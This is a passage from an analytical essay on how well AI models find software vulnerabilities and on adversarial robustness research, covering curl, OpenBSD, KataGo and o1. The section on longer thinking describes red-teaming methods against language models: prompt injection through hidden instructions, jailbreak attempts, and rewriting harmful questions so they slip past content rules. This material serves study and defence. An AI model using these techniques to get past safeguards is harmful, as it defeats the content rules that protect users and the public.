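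When a model guesses wrong about a flaw, it wastes only some computing time. AddressSanitizer, a tool for detecting memory errors, stops a program when it touches memory that it shouldn't, so a plausible but imaginary memory flaw fails the test. *Partnering with Mozilla to improve Firefox's security* (Ben Asher, Lucas and colleagues, 2026) calls such a tool a task verifier and reports that Claude works best when it has one. The model draws on broad knowledge to make its guesses, but the verifier is a narrow program that contains no information about attackers.

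To cover a whole program, the researchers first have the model rate each file from 1 to 5. A file that only defines constants gets a 1, and one that handles logins or reads data from the internet gets a 5. Separate copies of the model then search the files for vulnerabilities, starting with the highest-rated, and a final copy judges whether each report is real and important. The ratings imply a very simple attacker model, in which someone outside controls the program's input. They don't depend on who that person is or what he wants.

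Fuzzing often ends with the same kind of check, but it starts from automatically generated inputs instead of a guess. FFmpeg, a library that many video services use, had a flaw that fuzzers missed for 16 years. The library numbers the slices of each video frame, and one of the possible numbers was also the code for "no slice". Ordinary video never gets near that number, and random test files are very unlikely to. But someone who reads the code can notice that the counter has no upper limit while the table that stores its values does, and Mythos Preview found this mismatch.

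The model can also change its method when one fails. Anthropic describes how the earlier model Claude Opus 4.6 searched for flaws in Ghostscript, a program that processes PDF files. The model found nothing by fuzzing or by reading the code. It then read the history of changes and found one that had fixed a security problem. It looked for other places that called the same function, found one that still seemed to have the problem, and made a file that crashed the program. Someone on a mailing list hosted by Openwall (2026) checked Anthropic's examples and found fixes for this flaw and two others in the projects' public code.

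### A 27-year-old flaw in OpenBSD

Mythos Preview found a 27-year-old flaw in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security. Carlini and colleagues explain how the flaw worked, and OpenBSD's developers have since fixed it.

Computers that exchange data over the internet number the bytes they send, and the receiver acknowledges what has arrived. If some data goes missing, the receiver can acknowledge separate ranges on either side of the gap. The sender keeps a list of the gaps, which OpenBSD's code calls holes. If the sender has sent bytes 1 to 20 and the receiver has acknowledged 1 to 10 and 15 to 20, the list has one hole, from 11 to 14. When another acknowledgement arrives, the code shrinks or deletes the holes that acknowledgement covers and adds a hole at the end of the list for any new gap.

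The code checked that the end of an acknowledged range was plausible, but not the start. This usually did no harm, since acknowledging bytes −5 to 10 has the same effect as acknowledging 1 to 10. The other weakness was in how the code added a hole. If the same acknowledgement had just deleted the only hole in the list, the code had nothing to attach the new one to, and the system would crash.

To delete the hole, the acknowledged range had to start at or before the hole, and to add another, it had to start after everything acknowledged so far. No number can meet both conditions in ordinary arithmetic, but these numbers have a fixed size and start again from zero when they run out, like the hours on a clock. One o'clock comes after eleven if the two times are known to be close together, but if they may be many hours apart, the clock face doesn't show which came first. OpenBSD's comparison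 was likewise correct only for numbers that were close together. Because the code didn't check the start of the range, it could be far enough from the other numbers for both tests to succeed.

None of these facts is obscure, but a reviewer had to notice the missing check, doubt a comparison that is correct in normal use, and see that together they made a supposedly unreachable line of code reachable. The search that found the vulnerability took about a thousand runs, cost less than $20,000 in total, and produced several dozen other findings. The successful run cost under $50, but nobody could have known beforehand which run would succeed.

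### What the developers report

Google was among the first to report such a result. In November 2024 it announced that Big Sleep, an agent built by its security and AI researchers, had found a memory flaw in the database program SQLite before the flawed code reached an official release. As with Ghostscript, the search started from earlier changes to the code.

DARPA, the US defence research agency, ran a larger test, the AI Cyber Challenge. In the August 2025 final, seven teams entered systems that had to find and repair flaws without human help. The organisers had planted flaws in real open-source programs. By DARPA's count, the systems together found 54 of the planted flaws (86%) and repaired 43. They also found 18 flaws that were already in the programs.

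Microsoft's *Defense at AI speed* (2026) reports that several members of the winning team later joined Microsoft and worked on a system codenamed MDASH, which combines several models. iTnews' *Microsoft's MDASH AI vulnerability scanner finds four critical Windows RCEs* reports Microsoft's claim that MDASH found all 21 flaws planted in a private piece of software, with no false alarms. Microsoft uses this software to interview security researchers, so the flaws are presumably meant for a good candidate to find, unlike flaws planted by an attacker.

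Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.6 before releasing it in February 2026. The researchers gave the model debuggers and fuzzers but no instructions for using them, according to The Hacker News (2026). Axios' *Anthropic's new model is a pro at finding security flaws* (2026) reports that the model found more than 500 previously unknown vulnerabilities in open-source code and that people checked each one.

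Ben Asher and colleagues then spent two weeks searching the Firefox browser with the same model. The model reported its first flaw after twenty minutes. They covered nearly 6,000 files and sent 112 reports to Mozilla, which makes Firefox. These reports led to 22 recognised vulnerabilities, 14 of them high-severity, almost a fifth as many high-severity flaws as Mozilla fixed in all of 2025.

Carlini and colleagues write that all 112 reports were true positives, which is fair if any real bug counts. If only security vulnerabilities count, about one report in five qualifies, assuming that each vulnerability had its own report. Mozilla had asked for everything, including crashes that might not matter for security, so the lower figure is not a failure by the model. But a false alarm rate can depend heavily on what counts as a true positive.

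Anthropic made much larger claims for Mythos Preview, which it announced in April 2026, saying the model had found thousands of high- or critical-severity flaws. Security contractors paid by Anthropic reviewed 198 of the reports. They agreed exactly with the model's severity rating in 89% of cases and were within one level in 98%. However, the model had already filtered its own findings, and Anthropic sends the contractors the most serious ones, so these percentages are little evidence of how accurate the raw output was. Outsiders could check very few of the claims at the time because fewer than 1% of the flaws had been fully repaired. Anthropic published hashes of some of the unpublished reports so it can later prove it had them in April.

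### Outside tests

*Our evaluation of Claude Mythos Preview's cyber capabilities*, by the UK government's AI Security Institute, reports that the model did better than earlier models on security puzzles and significantly better on simulated attacks with many steps. According to Help Net Security's *Testing reveals Claude Mythos's offensive capabilities and limits*, the institute found that the model could not reliably attack well-defended networks on its own.

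The institute later tested a stronger version of Mythos Preview on Cooling Tower, one of its simulated networks, where an attacker has to find and use a chain of weaknesses in order. The model completed the chain in 3 of 10 attempts, and no other model had completed it, according to Epoch AI's *Are Mythos' cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026).

These tests are independent, but they measure attacking, which is not a code reviewer's job. Epoch AI, a research organisation that tracks AI progress, had the same problem when it combined about fifteen security benchmarks, because most of them measure how well a model can exploit a known flaw. On this combined measure, Mythos Preview was about seven months ahead of the trend since early 2025 (90% confidence interval 3 to 13 months). Epoch AI knew of no benchmark for finding flaws in source code on which the best models did not already score close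 to the maximum.

Epoch AI looked at how many flaws 21 large organisations published. The number of high and critical vulnerabilities was 142% above the 2025 average in April 2026 and 262% above it in May. But Anthropic had offered its partners up to $100 million in free use of Mythos Preview, so more searching, rather than better searching, could explain some or all of the rise. Epoch AI concluded that earlier models were already very good at finding flaws, and that Mythos Preview's advantage was probably that it raised fewer false alarms and judged severity better.

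### One flaw in curl

The most detailed outside account is *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability* (Stenberg, 2026), by Daniel Stenberg, who leads curl, a data-transfer tool that runs on billions of devices. It describes a report that someone with access to the model produced for the project in May. The report covered 178,000 lines of code and listed five "confirmed" security vulnerabilities. After several hours of work, curl's security team accepted one as a low-severity vulnerability, judged another to be an ordinary bug, and found that the other three were behaviour that curl's documentation already described.

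The report also listed about twenty bugs that it did not class as vulnerabilities, and almost all were real. The model was therefore good at recognising when the code did something odd, but worse at judging whether that was a security problem. That judgement requires knowing what curl promises its users, which is why harmful effects are difficult to list in advance. Stenberg (2026) made the same criticism of AI tools in general in *High volume AI vulnerability reports*, a set of slides from October, calling them great at finding bugs but "still weak at understanding security context".

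Stenberg saw no sign that Mythos was much better than its predecessors, but the comparison puts Mythos at a disadvantage because the easier flaws in curl were already gone. Over the previous eight to ten months, other AI tools had led to between two and three hundred fixes, including fixes for perhaps a dozen vulnerabilities.

Many other vulnerabilities remained, though. When the report arrived, curl had published 188. By version 8.22.0, a few months later, it counted 215 security fixes, and Stenberg (2026) announced that 22 more would follow on 14 October, including one of high severity. Some of these flaws may have entered the code after May, and he does not say who or what found them. But unless most of them were new, the May search missed dozens. Premise 4 requires a superhuman reviewer to miss nothing that a capable attacker could find, and this one fell far short of that on a program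 that people had already searched thoroughly.

### The cost of checking reports

According to Stenberg's slides, many of the early reports from the public were what he calls slop. One described a function that did not exist and a crash that had not happened. In early 2026, curl stopped paying rewards for reports because the rewards attracted so much slop. The later reports were mostly competent, but there were far more of them, and many were duplicates because several people had run the same tools. Each report takes the maintainers hours or days to assess, and a good one takes longer than a bad one. In July, curl accepted no vulnerability reports so that its maintainers could rest.

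According to Sabah's *Yapay zeka kirliliği siber güvenliği vurdu* (2026), Google suspended its rewards for flaws in open-source software because of a surge in AI-generated reports, most of them invalid. 24-ore's *Raportet e sigurisë të krijuara me AI po mbingarkojnë mirëmbajtësit e programeve* reports that Michael Aiello, who leads OpenAI's work on cybersecurity, thinks the problem is harder than weeding out invalid reports, because many describe real defects and maintainers have to work out which ones matter. OpenAI's own programme works with maintainers throughout and offers them tested repairs. Maintainers have accepted 458 of 661 repairs (69%).

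Stenberg quotes figures from the company Contrast Security for an AI search of a large business application. The search cost $315 and produced 3,560 findings. Reviewing the findings, at half an hour of an engineer's time each, cost about $128,000, or 400 times as much as the search.

Developers can do more of this filtering before anyone contacts a maintainer. *Maintainers don't need more AI bug reports. They need fixes* (Wolf and Cochran, 2026) describes a pilot in which GitHub and Microsoft ran MDASH on six open-source projects and sent them 99 private reports. The system started with 9,791 findings, according to Centrum.cz's *Umělá inteligence ohrožuje lidi, na kterých stojí Linux i další klíčový software*. Software removed duplicates and sorted the rest, and security specialists then checked what was left. The projects had fixed 55 of the reported problems by 15 November. Only about 1%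 of the findings became reports, but many findings were duplicates, so the other 99% were not necessarily wrong.

These systems depend on people to decide which bugs are important, because there is no test of importance as simple as using a crash to confirm that a bug is real.

### Small models shown the right code

*AI Cybersecurity After Mythos* reports that smaller language models often succeed at finding software flaws, which suggests that the task doesn't require the most general model available. Stanislav Fort, founder and chief scientist of the security company AISLE, took flaws that Anthropic had publicised, cut out the relevant code, and gave it to eight smaller or cheaper models. All eight recognised a flaw in the operating system FreeBSD, including GPT-OSS-20b, which uses only 3.6 billion of its parameters at a time and costs 11 cents per million tokens (pieces of words). Only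 GPT-OSS-120b fully explained the flaw in OpenBSD, another operating system.

After a reader raised the question, Fort also tested whether the models could tell when the FreeBSD flaw had been repaired. Six models judged both the flawed and repaired versions three times.

| Model | Flawed code judged vulnerable | Repaired code judged safe | Grade on the OpenBSD flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-120b | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 | A+ |
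| Qwen3 32B | 3 of 3 | 2 of 3 | F |
| Codestral 2508 | 3 of 3 | 1 of 3 | D |
| Kimi K2 | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 | A− |
| DeepSeek R1 | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 | B− |
| GPT-OSS-20b | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 | C |

The six models found the flaw in every run, but so would a program that called all code vulnerable. The middle columns show that the models also wrongly called the repaired code vulnerable in 12 of 18 runs. Only GPT-OSS-120b reliably told the two versions apart. At that combined error rate, in ordinary code with one flawed function in a thousand, the models would raise about 666 false alarms for each real flaw. The rate for ordinary code is probably lower, because the repaired function is unusually hard to judge when it looks almost exactly like the flawed one.

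AISLE sells a system that can use many different models, so it has a commercial interest in Fort's argument that the system around the model matters more than the model. Fort acknowledges the limits of his test, including that the models received the flawed function directly, often with hints such as to consider numbers that wrap around. A commenter on *Small models also found the vulnerabilities that Mythos found* compared this to looking for a needle in a couple of pieces of straw instead of a haystack.

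Semgrep, which also sells security tools, compared how models performed when given only the flawed function and when given the whole file in *Needles and haystacks*. The best open model, Qwen 3.6, identified the problem in 7 of 8 attempts with the function alone, but found the right function in only 1 of 8 with the whole file. Three leading large models all succeeded with the isolated function, but on whole files, Claude Opus and Qwen tended to succeed in different places. The Decoder's *The myth of Claude Mythos crumbles* describes another company's attempt to reproduce the OpenBSD result. Claude Opus 4.6 found the flaw in all three runs, and GPT-5.4 missed it every time.

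Fort answers the haystack objection by arguing that a well-built system narrows the search itself. AISLE's *System Over Model* describes a simple tool that scans an entire codebase with small models, without being told where to look. The tool detected the FreeBSD flaw repeatedly and found new bugs that FreeBSD's maintainers confirmed. AISLE mentions only candidates for OpenBSD, where the reasoning is harder. Small models are cheap enough to run on all the code, so choosing which code to examine matters less if someone can sort through the alarms. That makes false alarms the main obstacle, as they are for intrusion detectors.

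Even if AISLE is right, its result concerns how large a model must be, not how general. GPT-OSS-20b is a small model, but still a general one that can discuss history or write a letter. A proper test of premise 5 would need a model trained only on code and its flaws. The closest in Fort's test is Codestral, which specialises in code. It did no better than the others, but it is only one model and was also trained on ordinary text, so this is weak evidence.

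### Where the ability came from

Carlini and colleagues at Anthropic write that they did not explicitly train Mythos Preview for these abilities, and that the abilities emerged from "general improvements in code, reasoning, and autonomy". This supports premise 5 to some extent, since it suggests that people can get a better reviewer by building a more capable general model.

The statement supports the premise less than it may seem to. Outsiders can't inspect the training, and the word "explicitly" doesn't rule out that the model learned from a great deal of security writing. Writing correct code and finding incorrect code are also closely related, so carrying a gain over from one to the other is not a large step. The statement shows that general training helps produce good reviewers, but not that they require it.

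What the models do with a program is better evidence of breadth. According to Stenberg, AI tools can notice when a comment doesn't match the code, spot wrong assumptions about other people's libraries, and check code against the published rules of an internet protocol, none of which older analysers can do. All of this depends on reading English and knowing about things outside the program. Stenberg considers the AI tools significantly better than any traditional analyser. This comparison matters to the argument because traditional analysers are narrow tools, though it comes from code that they had already checked many times.

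Some of the success might come from memory rather than reasoning, since a model that reproduces a published flaw may only be remembering it. Ben Asher and colleagues worried about this when Opus 4.6 reproduced many old Firefox vulnerabilities, so they went on to look for unreported ones, which the model could not have memorized. Microsoft's *Beyond the benchmark* (2026) makes a similar point about MDASH, which works on internal parts of Windows that Microsoft says no model saw in training.

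But a new flaw can be of a known kind. Stenberg has not yet seen an AI tool report a previously unknown kind of vulnerability, and Epoch AI reports that Mozilla said much the same of Mythos. The OpenBSD flaw combines a missing check, an integer overflow and a null pointer. All three are textbook errors, but their combination was new. Most flaws that people find are also of known kinds, so the models' reliance on known kinds does not distinguish them from human reviewers.

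In another test, Fort gave more than 25 models a short program that looks like a textbook vulnerability but is harmless because it never uses what the user typed. Many large models called it vulnerable, apparently because of the resemblance, while some small ones followed the data and correctly called it harmless. Newer models, including Opus 4.6, pass. *Trust Me, I Know This Function* (Bernstein, Beste and colleagues, 2025) found that familiar-looking code can also mislead language models into overlooking what a program does.

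### Flaws that nobody intended

A vulnerability is a fact about what a program does when it receives certain inputs, so a reviewer can establish that it exists without knowing how it got there. Mythos Preview could find the flaw in the code for OpenBSD's list of holes without determining whether the programmers who wrote it in the 1990s had introduced the flaw deliberately, which they presumably had not.

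For this kind of review, premise 3 is mostly false. The reviewer must represent an input that does damage, but not the strategy or goal of the person who would send it. This holds even if someone planted the flaw, as in the hypocrite commits, because a model that found the memory error could reject the patch without suspecting anyone.

A backdoor like the one in xz is different because AddressSanitizer would not detect it. A model could still read the code and flag that a compression library should not change how logins work, but it would be relying on its understanding of what the software is for, with no crash to confirm the finding. The Mythos report did badly on this kind of judgement in curl.

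The published results therefore come mostly from vulnerabilities that a machine can confirm. Carlini and colleagues say they concentrated on memory errors partly because these are easy to verify. Nobody has published a comparable count of hidden backdoors that language models found in real projects. The planted flaws in DARPA's contest and Microsoft's test are not a substitute, because the people who planted them were not trying to get past a particular model. A real attacker could do that by practising on a public model.

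### Whether a good reviewer is also a good attacker

In March 2026 it looked as if a model might be good at finding software flaws without being good at exploiting them. Ben Asher and colleagues gave Opus 4.6 the Firefox flaws it had found and asked it to write programs that exploited them. The model succeeded twice in several hundred attempts, which cost about $4,000, and only in a test environment without some of the browser's normal protections. The researchers concluded that defenders had the advantage for the time being, but doubted it would last long.

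It lasted about a month, until Carlini and colleagues repeated the experiment with Mythos Preview, which produced 181 working exploits. They attribute this to the same general improvements that made the model better at repairing flaws. Cheng, Lucas and colleagues (2026) write in *Measuring LLMs' ability to develop exploits* that they were most concerned by the model's ability to combine several weaknesses into a complete attack.

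Another Anthropic test shows that the skills of crashing a program and taking control of it can still grow at different rates. The researchers ran each model once on about 7,000 entry points in open-source programs and graded the worst crash from each run on a five-level severity scale. Opus 4.6 caused roughly 250 to 275 crashes in the two mildest grades, and the newer Mythos Preview caused 595, a little more than twice as many. In the most serious grade, where an attacker takes full control of the program, the count rose from none to ten.

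Fort argues that most defensive work consists of finding, sorting and repairing flaws, and that a defender seldom has to build a complete attack. In his tests, the smaller models reasoned well about whether the FreeBSD flaw was exploitable, but none found the method that Mythos had used to exploit it. A company could therefore use a reviewer that is mediocre at building attacks, if it accepts that the reviewer will sometimes misjudge how serious a flaw is.

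That choice leads to more false alarms. Epoch AI suggests that Mythos Preview raises so few of them partly because it is good at writing exploits, since a working exploit proves that a flaw is real. An exploit can also show that several minor flaws add up to a serious one, which helped two of Anthropic's partners decide what to repair first. A reviewer that is better at writing such exploits would also be more useful to an attacker who obtained it.

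Attackers and defenders differ more in what they must do with the flaws they find. An attacker needs only one flaw it can exploit, while a defender has to repair every flaw that matters without breaking anything, then get users to install the new version. Anthropic gave selected defenders early access to Mythos Preview for this reason, and Carlini and colleagues expect defenders to benefit more in the long run, as they did from fuzzing.

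A repair can also help attackers. InfoQ's *AI Agents Are Disrupting Open Source Security Disclosure* (2026) reports Anil Madhavapeddy's argument that AI agents can turn public clues about a flaw into a working attack, which leaves projects less time to release a fix. Opus 4.6 used such a clue in Ghostscript, where an old security fix led it to a similar flaw nearby. When the Openwall reader looked for the fix for that second flaw, it was already in the public code but not yet in any Ghostscript release.

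## Whether robustness requires larger and more general models

The language models that find software flaws are both large and general, but either property might do little against an attacker who targets the reviewer itself. A robust system keeps giving the right answers when someone chooses its inputs to make it fail. Robustness might require more parameters (the numbers a model learns in training), more computation for each answer, or competence in more subjects. A larger model is not necessarily more general, since a spam filter could have a trillion parameters and still only be able to detect spam. Premise 5 holds only if robustness requires competence in more subjects.

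### Fitting data smoothly

An attacker can often fool an image classifier by changing the pixels so slightly that people don't notice. One protection is to make the classifier's output change slowly as its input changes. The Lipschitz constant of a function f measures this. It is the smallest number L for which

|f(x) − f(x′)| ≤ L ‖x − x′‖

for every pair of inputs x and x′. If L is small, a small change to the input can only have a small effect.

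Bubeck and Sellke (2021), in *A Universal Law of Robustness via Isoperimetry*, proved that smoothness requires a large model. Suppose a model with p parameters learns from n examples, each consisting of d numbers and a noisy label. About n parameters are generally enough to fit the labels. But if the model fits them more closely than the noise should allow, then, ignoring constants and logarithmic factors,

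L ≥ √(nd/p).

With 10,000 examples of 100 numbers each, a model with 10,000 parameters can fit the labels, but its Lipschitz constant will be at least about 10. To bring that down to 1, the model needs about a million parameters, one for each number in the data.

The proof relies on isoperimetry, a property of high-dimensional data which means that a smooth function stays close to its average on nearly all inputs. Such a function is unlikely to match random labels. If its Lipschitz constant is L, the chance that it matches all n labels is at most about e^(−nd/L²). A model with p parameters can represent roughly e^p noticeably different functions, so one of them is likely to fit only if p is at least about nd/L², which rearranges to the bound.

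Isoperimetry holds for points spread evenly over a high-dimensional sphere, for example, but it may not hold for real data. *A Law of Robustness beyond Isoperimetry* (2022) found that on the order of n parameters may be enough for data in general. The theorem also requires noisy labels and parameters of limited size, and it may not apply to a model whose training stops once its error reaches the noise level. Later work has relaxed some of these conditions. *Four Extensions of the Universal Law of Robustness* (2026) proves versions for models with several outputs and for examples that depend on each other, and *Does Order Matter* (2026) describes an extension to the error measures that classifiers commonly use.

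Bubeck and Sellke compared their bound with an earlier experiment on MNIST, a collection of 60,000 images of handwritten digits. Each image has 784 pixels but the images vary in far fewer ways, so they took d to be between 15 and 150. The bound then requires between one and ten million parameters. In the experiment, accuracy under attack jumped from about 10% to 90% at around 200,000 parameters and reached 95% at around three million. For ImageNet, a much larger collection of photographs, they estimated that 10 to 100 billion parameters were needed, while robustly trained networks at the time had at most about a billion. They called these comparisons highly speculative.

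Even where the theorem applies, it concerns size and has no bearing on breadth. Bubeck and Sellke themselves describe a smooth model that needs only n(d + 1) parameters. It stores every example with its label and computes

f(x) = Σ yᵢ g(‖x − xᵢ‖),

where g is a smooth bump that equals 1 at distance 0 and falls to 0 at distance 1. This is a lookup table with soft edges. It meets the requirement without understanding anything, and it returns 0 for any input that is far from all the stored examples.

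The lookup table also shows that robustness requires more than smoothness, because a model can be smooth around its training examples and wrong about everything else. Smoothness limits only the effect of small changes, and a spammer can make a large change by adding a hundred innocent words or rewriting the whole advertisement.

### Image classifiers under attack

Developers usually make classifiers robust through adversarial training, in which they attack the model during training and teach it the correct answers to the attacked inputs. *Adversarial Robustness Limits via Scaling-Law and Human-Alignment Studies* (Bartoldson, Diffenderfer and colleagues, 2024) measured how much this method improves with larger models and more data. The tests used CIFAR10, a collection of small pictures of ten kinds of animals and vehicles, and let the attacker change each pixel value by up to 8/255 of its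 range. The best classifiers got nearly 100% of the ordinary pictures right, but only 71% of the attacked ones.

The researchers trained models of many sizes and fitted their results to a formula which, for ideal training data, is

loss = A/N^α + B/D^β + E,

where N is the number of parameters, D is the number of training images, and E is the error that remains however large N and D become. Their best model got 74% of the attacked pictures right. The formula predicted that accuracy would level off near 90%, and that getting there would take about 10³⁰ arithmetic operations, or 3,000 years on 25,000 of the fastest chips then available.

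Adding parameters was not always the best use of computation. A model with 79 million parameters, trained on more images, did slightly better than the previous record holder, which had 267 million parameters and used the same amount of computation.

Part of the remaining error came from the test itself. Three members of the team reviewed the 2,629 attacked pictures their best model got wrong, and GPT-4 classified them too. The team judged that 727 of these pictures no longer clearly showed the object in the label, and that some clearly showed a different one. They estimated that people would classify about 90% of all the attacked pictures correctly. Without the 727, the estimate was 96% for people and 79% for the model. If an attacker turns a picture of a horse into a picture of something else, general understanding can't help a classifier match the label, because the label is now wrong.

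Larger models have since done fairly well on ImageNet. *Trading Inference-Time Compute for Adversarial Robustness* (Zaremba, Nitishinskaya and colleagues, 2025) mentions a 2024 classifier with about a billion parameters that got 71% of attacked pictures right, although the attacker could change each pixel only half as much as in the CIFAR10 test. The classifier is at least ten times smaller than Bubeck and Sellke's estimate for a good robust model, but it does not refute their estimate because it still got 29% of the attacked pictures wrong.

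### Larger language models

In *Scaling Trends in Language Model Robustness*, Howe, McKenzie and colleagues (2024) tested language models with 7.6 million to 14 billion parameters. They trained most of the models to sort text into two classes, such as spam and legitimate mail. Their main attack added ten tokens to the end of a text, using the model's internal calculations to search for tokens that would change its classification. The smallest model sorted 98% of ordinary email correctly and the largest did hardly better, so larger models could show an advantage only under attack.

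Without adversarial training, larger models were not reliably more robust. On film reviews, the attack succeeded nearly every time against the smallest model and less than 20% of the time against one with 12 billion parameters. On spam, however, it succeeded more often against a model with 6.7 billion parameters than against one with 124 million. When models had to judge which of two words was longer, size made no difference.

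Adversarial training helped much more. In each round, the researchers attacked the current model, added 200 of the attacked texts to a pool, and trained the model on a mix of these and ordinary texts. On several tasks, five rounds reduced the attack's success rate from over 90% to under 20%, and further rounds brought it below 5% for models of every size. Large models needed fewer rounds than small ones but used more computation overall, because each round required much more.

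The researchers then moved the added tokens to test whether the models would still resist. When the tokens came 90% of the way through the text, the large models kept most of their resistance, while the small ones improved slowly or stopped improving. When the tokens came at the beginning, no model resisted reliably. Being larger therefore helped models resist an attack slightly different from the ones in training, but not one that differed more.

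Attackers can also use more compute. For every model size they studied, Howe and colleagues found that the compute needed for a successful attack grew less than proportionally with the compute used for adversarial training, so the attacker gained when both sides doubled their compute. If attack compute grew as the square root of defense compute, for example, a defender who used four times as much would only double what the attacker needed. Attacks on larger models took more compute to begin with. If that trend continued, attacking a sufficiently large model would take more compute than defending it, but this extrapolates well beyond the models they tested and assumes that attackers do not find a more efficient method.

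### Thinking for longer

A model can also use more computation when it answers. OpenAI's o1 models work through a problem in intermediate steps before they reply. Zaremba and colleagues at OpenAI varied how long two of these models spent on those steps. They gave the models no adversarial training for the tasks and no information about the attacks.

In one test, the model had to solve an arithmetic problem and ignore a marked section of the prompt. The attacker controlled that section and tried to make the model answer 42, for instance by filling it with many examples of problems answered with 42. Longer attacks succeeded more often, but at any given length, the success rate fell towards zero as the model thought for longer. The same happened in most settings when the attacker hid instructions in a web page the model had to read.

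Forty people also tried to make o1-preview break OpenAI's content rules, without knowing how long the model was thinking. They needed an average of 11.0 attempts at the lowest of five thinking-time settings, about 16 at each of the middle three, and 22.6 at the highest. Prompts that had worked at other settings worked 36% of the time at the lowest setting and 19% at the highest.

Thinking for longer sometimes failed or even backfired:

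- A small increase from a very low level could make an attack more successful, apparently because the model needed some computation to follow the attacker's pattern at all.
- One prompt persuaded the smaller model, o1-mini, to think less, which made it easier to fool. (A monitor could notice this, because unusually short thinking is easy to measure.)
- An attacker who could write directly into the model's internal representation of the text, which ordinary users cannot do, still succeeded often if he controlled enough of it.

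Longer thinking also did little to stop an attacker from obtaining information that could be misused. The attacker, another language model, rewrote each harmful question until nothing in it suggested a bad purpose. For example, a question about hiding a dangerous plan became a request for an educational comparison of privacy tools. Answering the new question did not clearly break the rules, so a model that applied them perfectly might still have answered. Zaremba and colleagues compare the model to a judge and the rules to the law, since more time helps a judge apply a clear law but does not remove loopholes from it.

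Longer thinking helps smaller models too. Wu, Xiang and colleagues (2025), in *Does More Inference-Time Compute Really Help Robustness?*, found similar gains in openly available models such as DeepSeek R1 and Qwen3. But when the attacker had access to the intermediate steps, more thinking consistently made the models less robust. A service that shows its reasoning to users may therefore lose the benefit.

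*Get RICH or Die Scaling* (2025) reports that extra thinking improves robustness most in models that are already fairly robust, for instance because of adversarial training, and that model size does not explain the difference. The paper hypothesizes that thinking helps more when the parts of an attack resemble the training data. If so, extra thinking adds to what a model has learned about attacks but can't replace it.

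These results give premise 5 some support, because the reasoning that protected the o1 models is the same reasoning they use for ordinary problems. But the experiments tested only general models, so they can't show that a narrow program wouldn't benefit from more computation. The Go program KataGo, for example, is narrow, and its user can give it as much computation as they like by letting it search longer.

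### A champion that loses to bad players

KataGo is a Go program that plays far better than any human. It learned by playing against itself, and it chooses each move by exploring possible continuations. The number of "visits" measures how much it explores. In *Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs*, Wang, Gleave and colleagues (2022) trained other programs, called adversaries, solely to beat KataGo. An adversary could query KataGo's network for the move it would make in any position, but could not see the network's parameters.

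The first adversary beat KataGo in 99.9% of games when KataGo did not search ahead. It won by getting KataGo to pass too early, which ended the game while the adversary was ahead on points. The researchers then added a rule that forbade KataGo to pass while passing could still change the result. The rule required no model of the opponent, and with it KataGo won all of the next 1,000 games against this adversary.

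The researchers then trained a second adversary, which lures KataGo into building a large ring of stones and then captures the ring. KataGo's estimate of its chance of winning typically stays above 99% until shortly before the capture, often until the move before. At 4,096 visits per move, KataGo is much stronger than the best human players, but the adversary won 97% of 1,000 games against it. At ten million visits, which can take over an hour per move on a good home computer, KataGo still lost 72% of 50 games. Training the adversary took 14% as much computation as training KataGo.

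This adversary is a poor Go player that loses to amateurs. One of the researchers, a Go expert, learned the trick from its games and won more than 90% of his games against a highly ranked KataGo program, without help from a computer. The adversary also won 6.1% of its games against Leela Zero and 3.5% against ELF OpenGo, two other superhuman programs that it had never trained against.

KataGo's developer responded by starting a small share of its practice games from positions with such rings. The original adversary then almost always lost. Tseng, McLean and colleagues (2024), in *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?*, tested this defence and two others. One put KataGo through nine rounds of training, each against an adversary that had learned to beat the previous version. The other replaced KataGo's kind of network, which builds up its view of the board from small areas, with a vision transformer,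 which can relate distant points directly. The researchers then trained new adversaries against each defended program.

| Defence | Trick used by the new adversary | Visits per move by the defended program | Games won by the adversary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Practice on ring positions, late 2023 | Two-stone gift | 512 | 91% |
| Practice on ring positions, May 2024 | Ring | 65,536 | 56% |
| Nine rounds, last adversary in the series | Ring | 65,536 | 42% |
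| Nine rounds, separately trained adversary | Ring | 512 | 81% |
| Nine rounds, separately trained adversary | Ring | 4,096 | 4% |
| Vision transformer | Ring | 65,536 | 78% |

In the two-stone trick, KataGo needlessly lets the adversary capture two stones, and a rule against repeating earlier positions then stops it from recapturing. KataGo had trained with this rule, and its network receives a list of the moves the rule forbids.

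The defences did make attacks harder. An adversary won 97% of games against the original KataGo at 4,096 visits, but the separately trained adversary won only 4% against the version that went through nine rounds. Even so, the last adversary in the series won 42% of games at a much higher search level, after using about a quarter as much computation as the defence.

### A missing concept or a gap in training

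According to Tseng and colleagues, KataGo and similar programs fail to represent a feature, the ring, that amateurs easily learn. People can explain the trick to a novice in a few words, and the novice can then defend against rings of any size or shape. KataGo trained on many rings and still lost to new ones that looked only slightly different to people. This looks like a lack of understanding, and if such understanding comes only with general cognition, a narrow program will always have weaknesses that an opponent can find.

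But KataGo's training on attacks may have been too limited. Tseng and colleagues found that defending against any fixed attack took little computation, and they suggest that training on a large enough collection of attacks might fully protect a Go program. In their nine rounds, finding new attacks took 18 times as much computation as learning to resist them, which limited how many kinds of ring the program was trained on. They recommend faster ways of finding attacks, and training methods that look for strategies no opponent can exploit, like those used for successful poker programs.

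The experiments do not settle which explanation is right, but neither one requires broad knowledge. The concept KataGo lacks is about Go, and knowing medicine or law would not supply it. People do better because they can learn a rule from a few examples and apply it to new cases. That ability is part of general reasoning, and it may well be the most efficient way to close such gaps. To prove it is the only way, someone would have to show that much more varied training also fails.

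The adversary is also evidence against premise 5. It can only play Go, and it beat a superhuman program with a strategy that loses to amateurs. The defender was at least as general as the attacker and at least as skilled at Go.

The result is still discouraging for other defenders. Years of play and targeted training have not removed a known weakness from KataGo, even though an attacker in Go can only place a stone or pass and the rules settle who has won. A code reviewer faces attackers with far more options and has no comparable rules to settle whether code is secure.

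### What competition teaches

KataGo became superhuman by playing against copies of itself, and Tseng and colleagues suspect that this contributed to its vulnerability to adversaries. A copy has the same blind spots as the original, so self-play provides no incentive to explore the positions that both misjudge.

Competition can nevertheless produce skills that the training objective doesn't specify. In *Emergent Tool Use From Multi-Agent Autocurricula* (Baker, Kanitscheider and colleagues, 2019), two teams of simulated agents at OpenAI played hide-and-seek in a world with movable boxes and ramps. Their only objective was to do well at the game. The hiders learned to build shelters from boxes, and the seekers then learned to use ramps to get over the obstacles, which put new pressure on the hiders. The researchers counted six such phases in the teams' strategies. This resembles the ratchet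 that Humphrey proposed for apes, except that the agents developed tool use rather than social skill.

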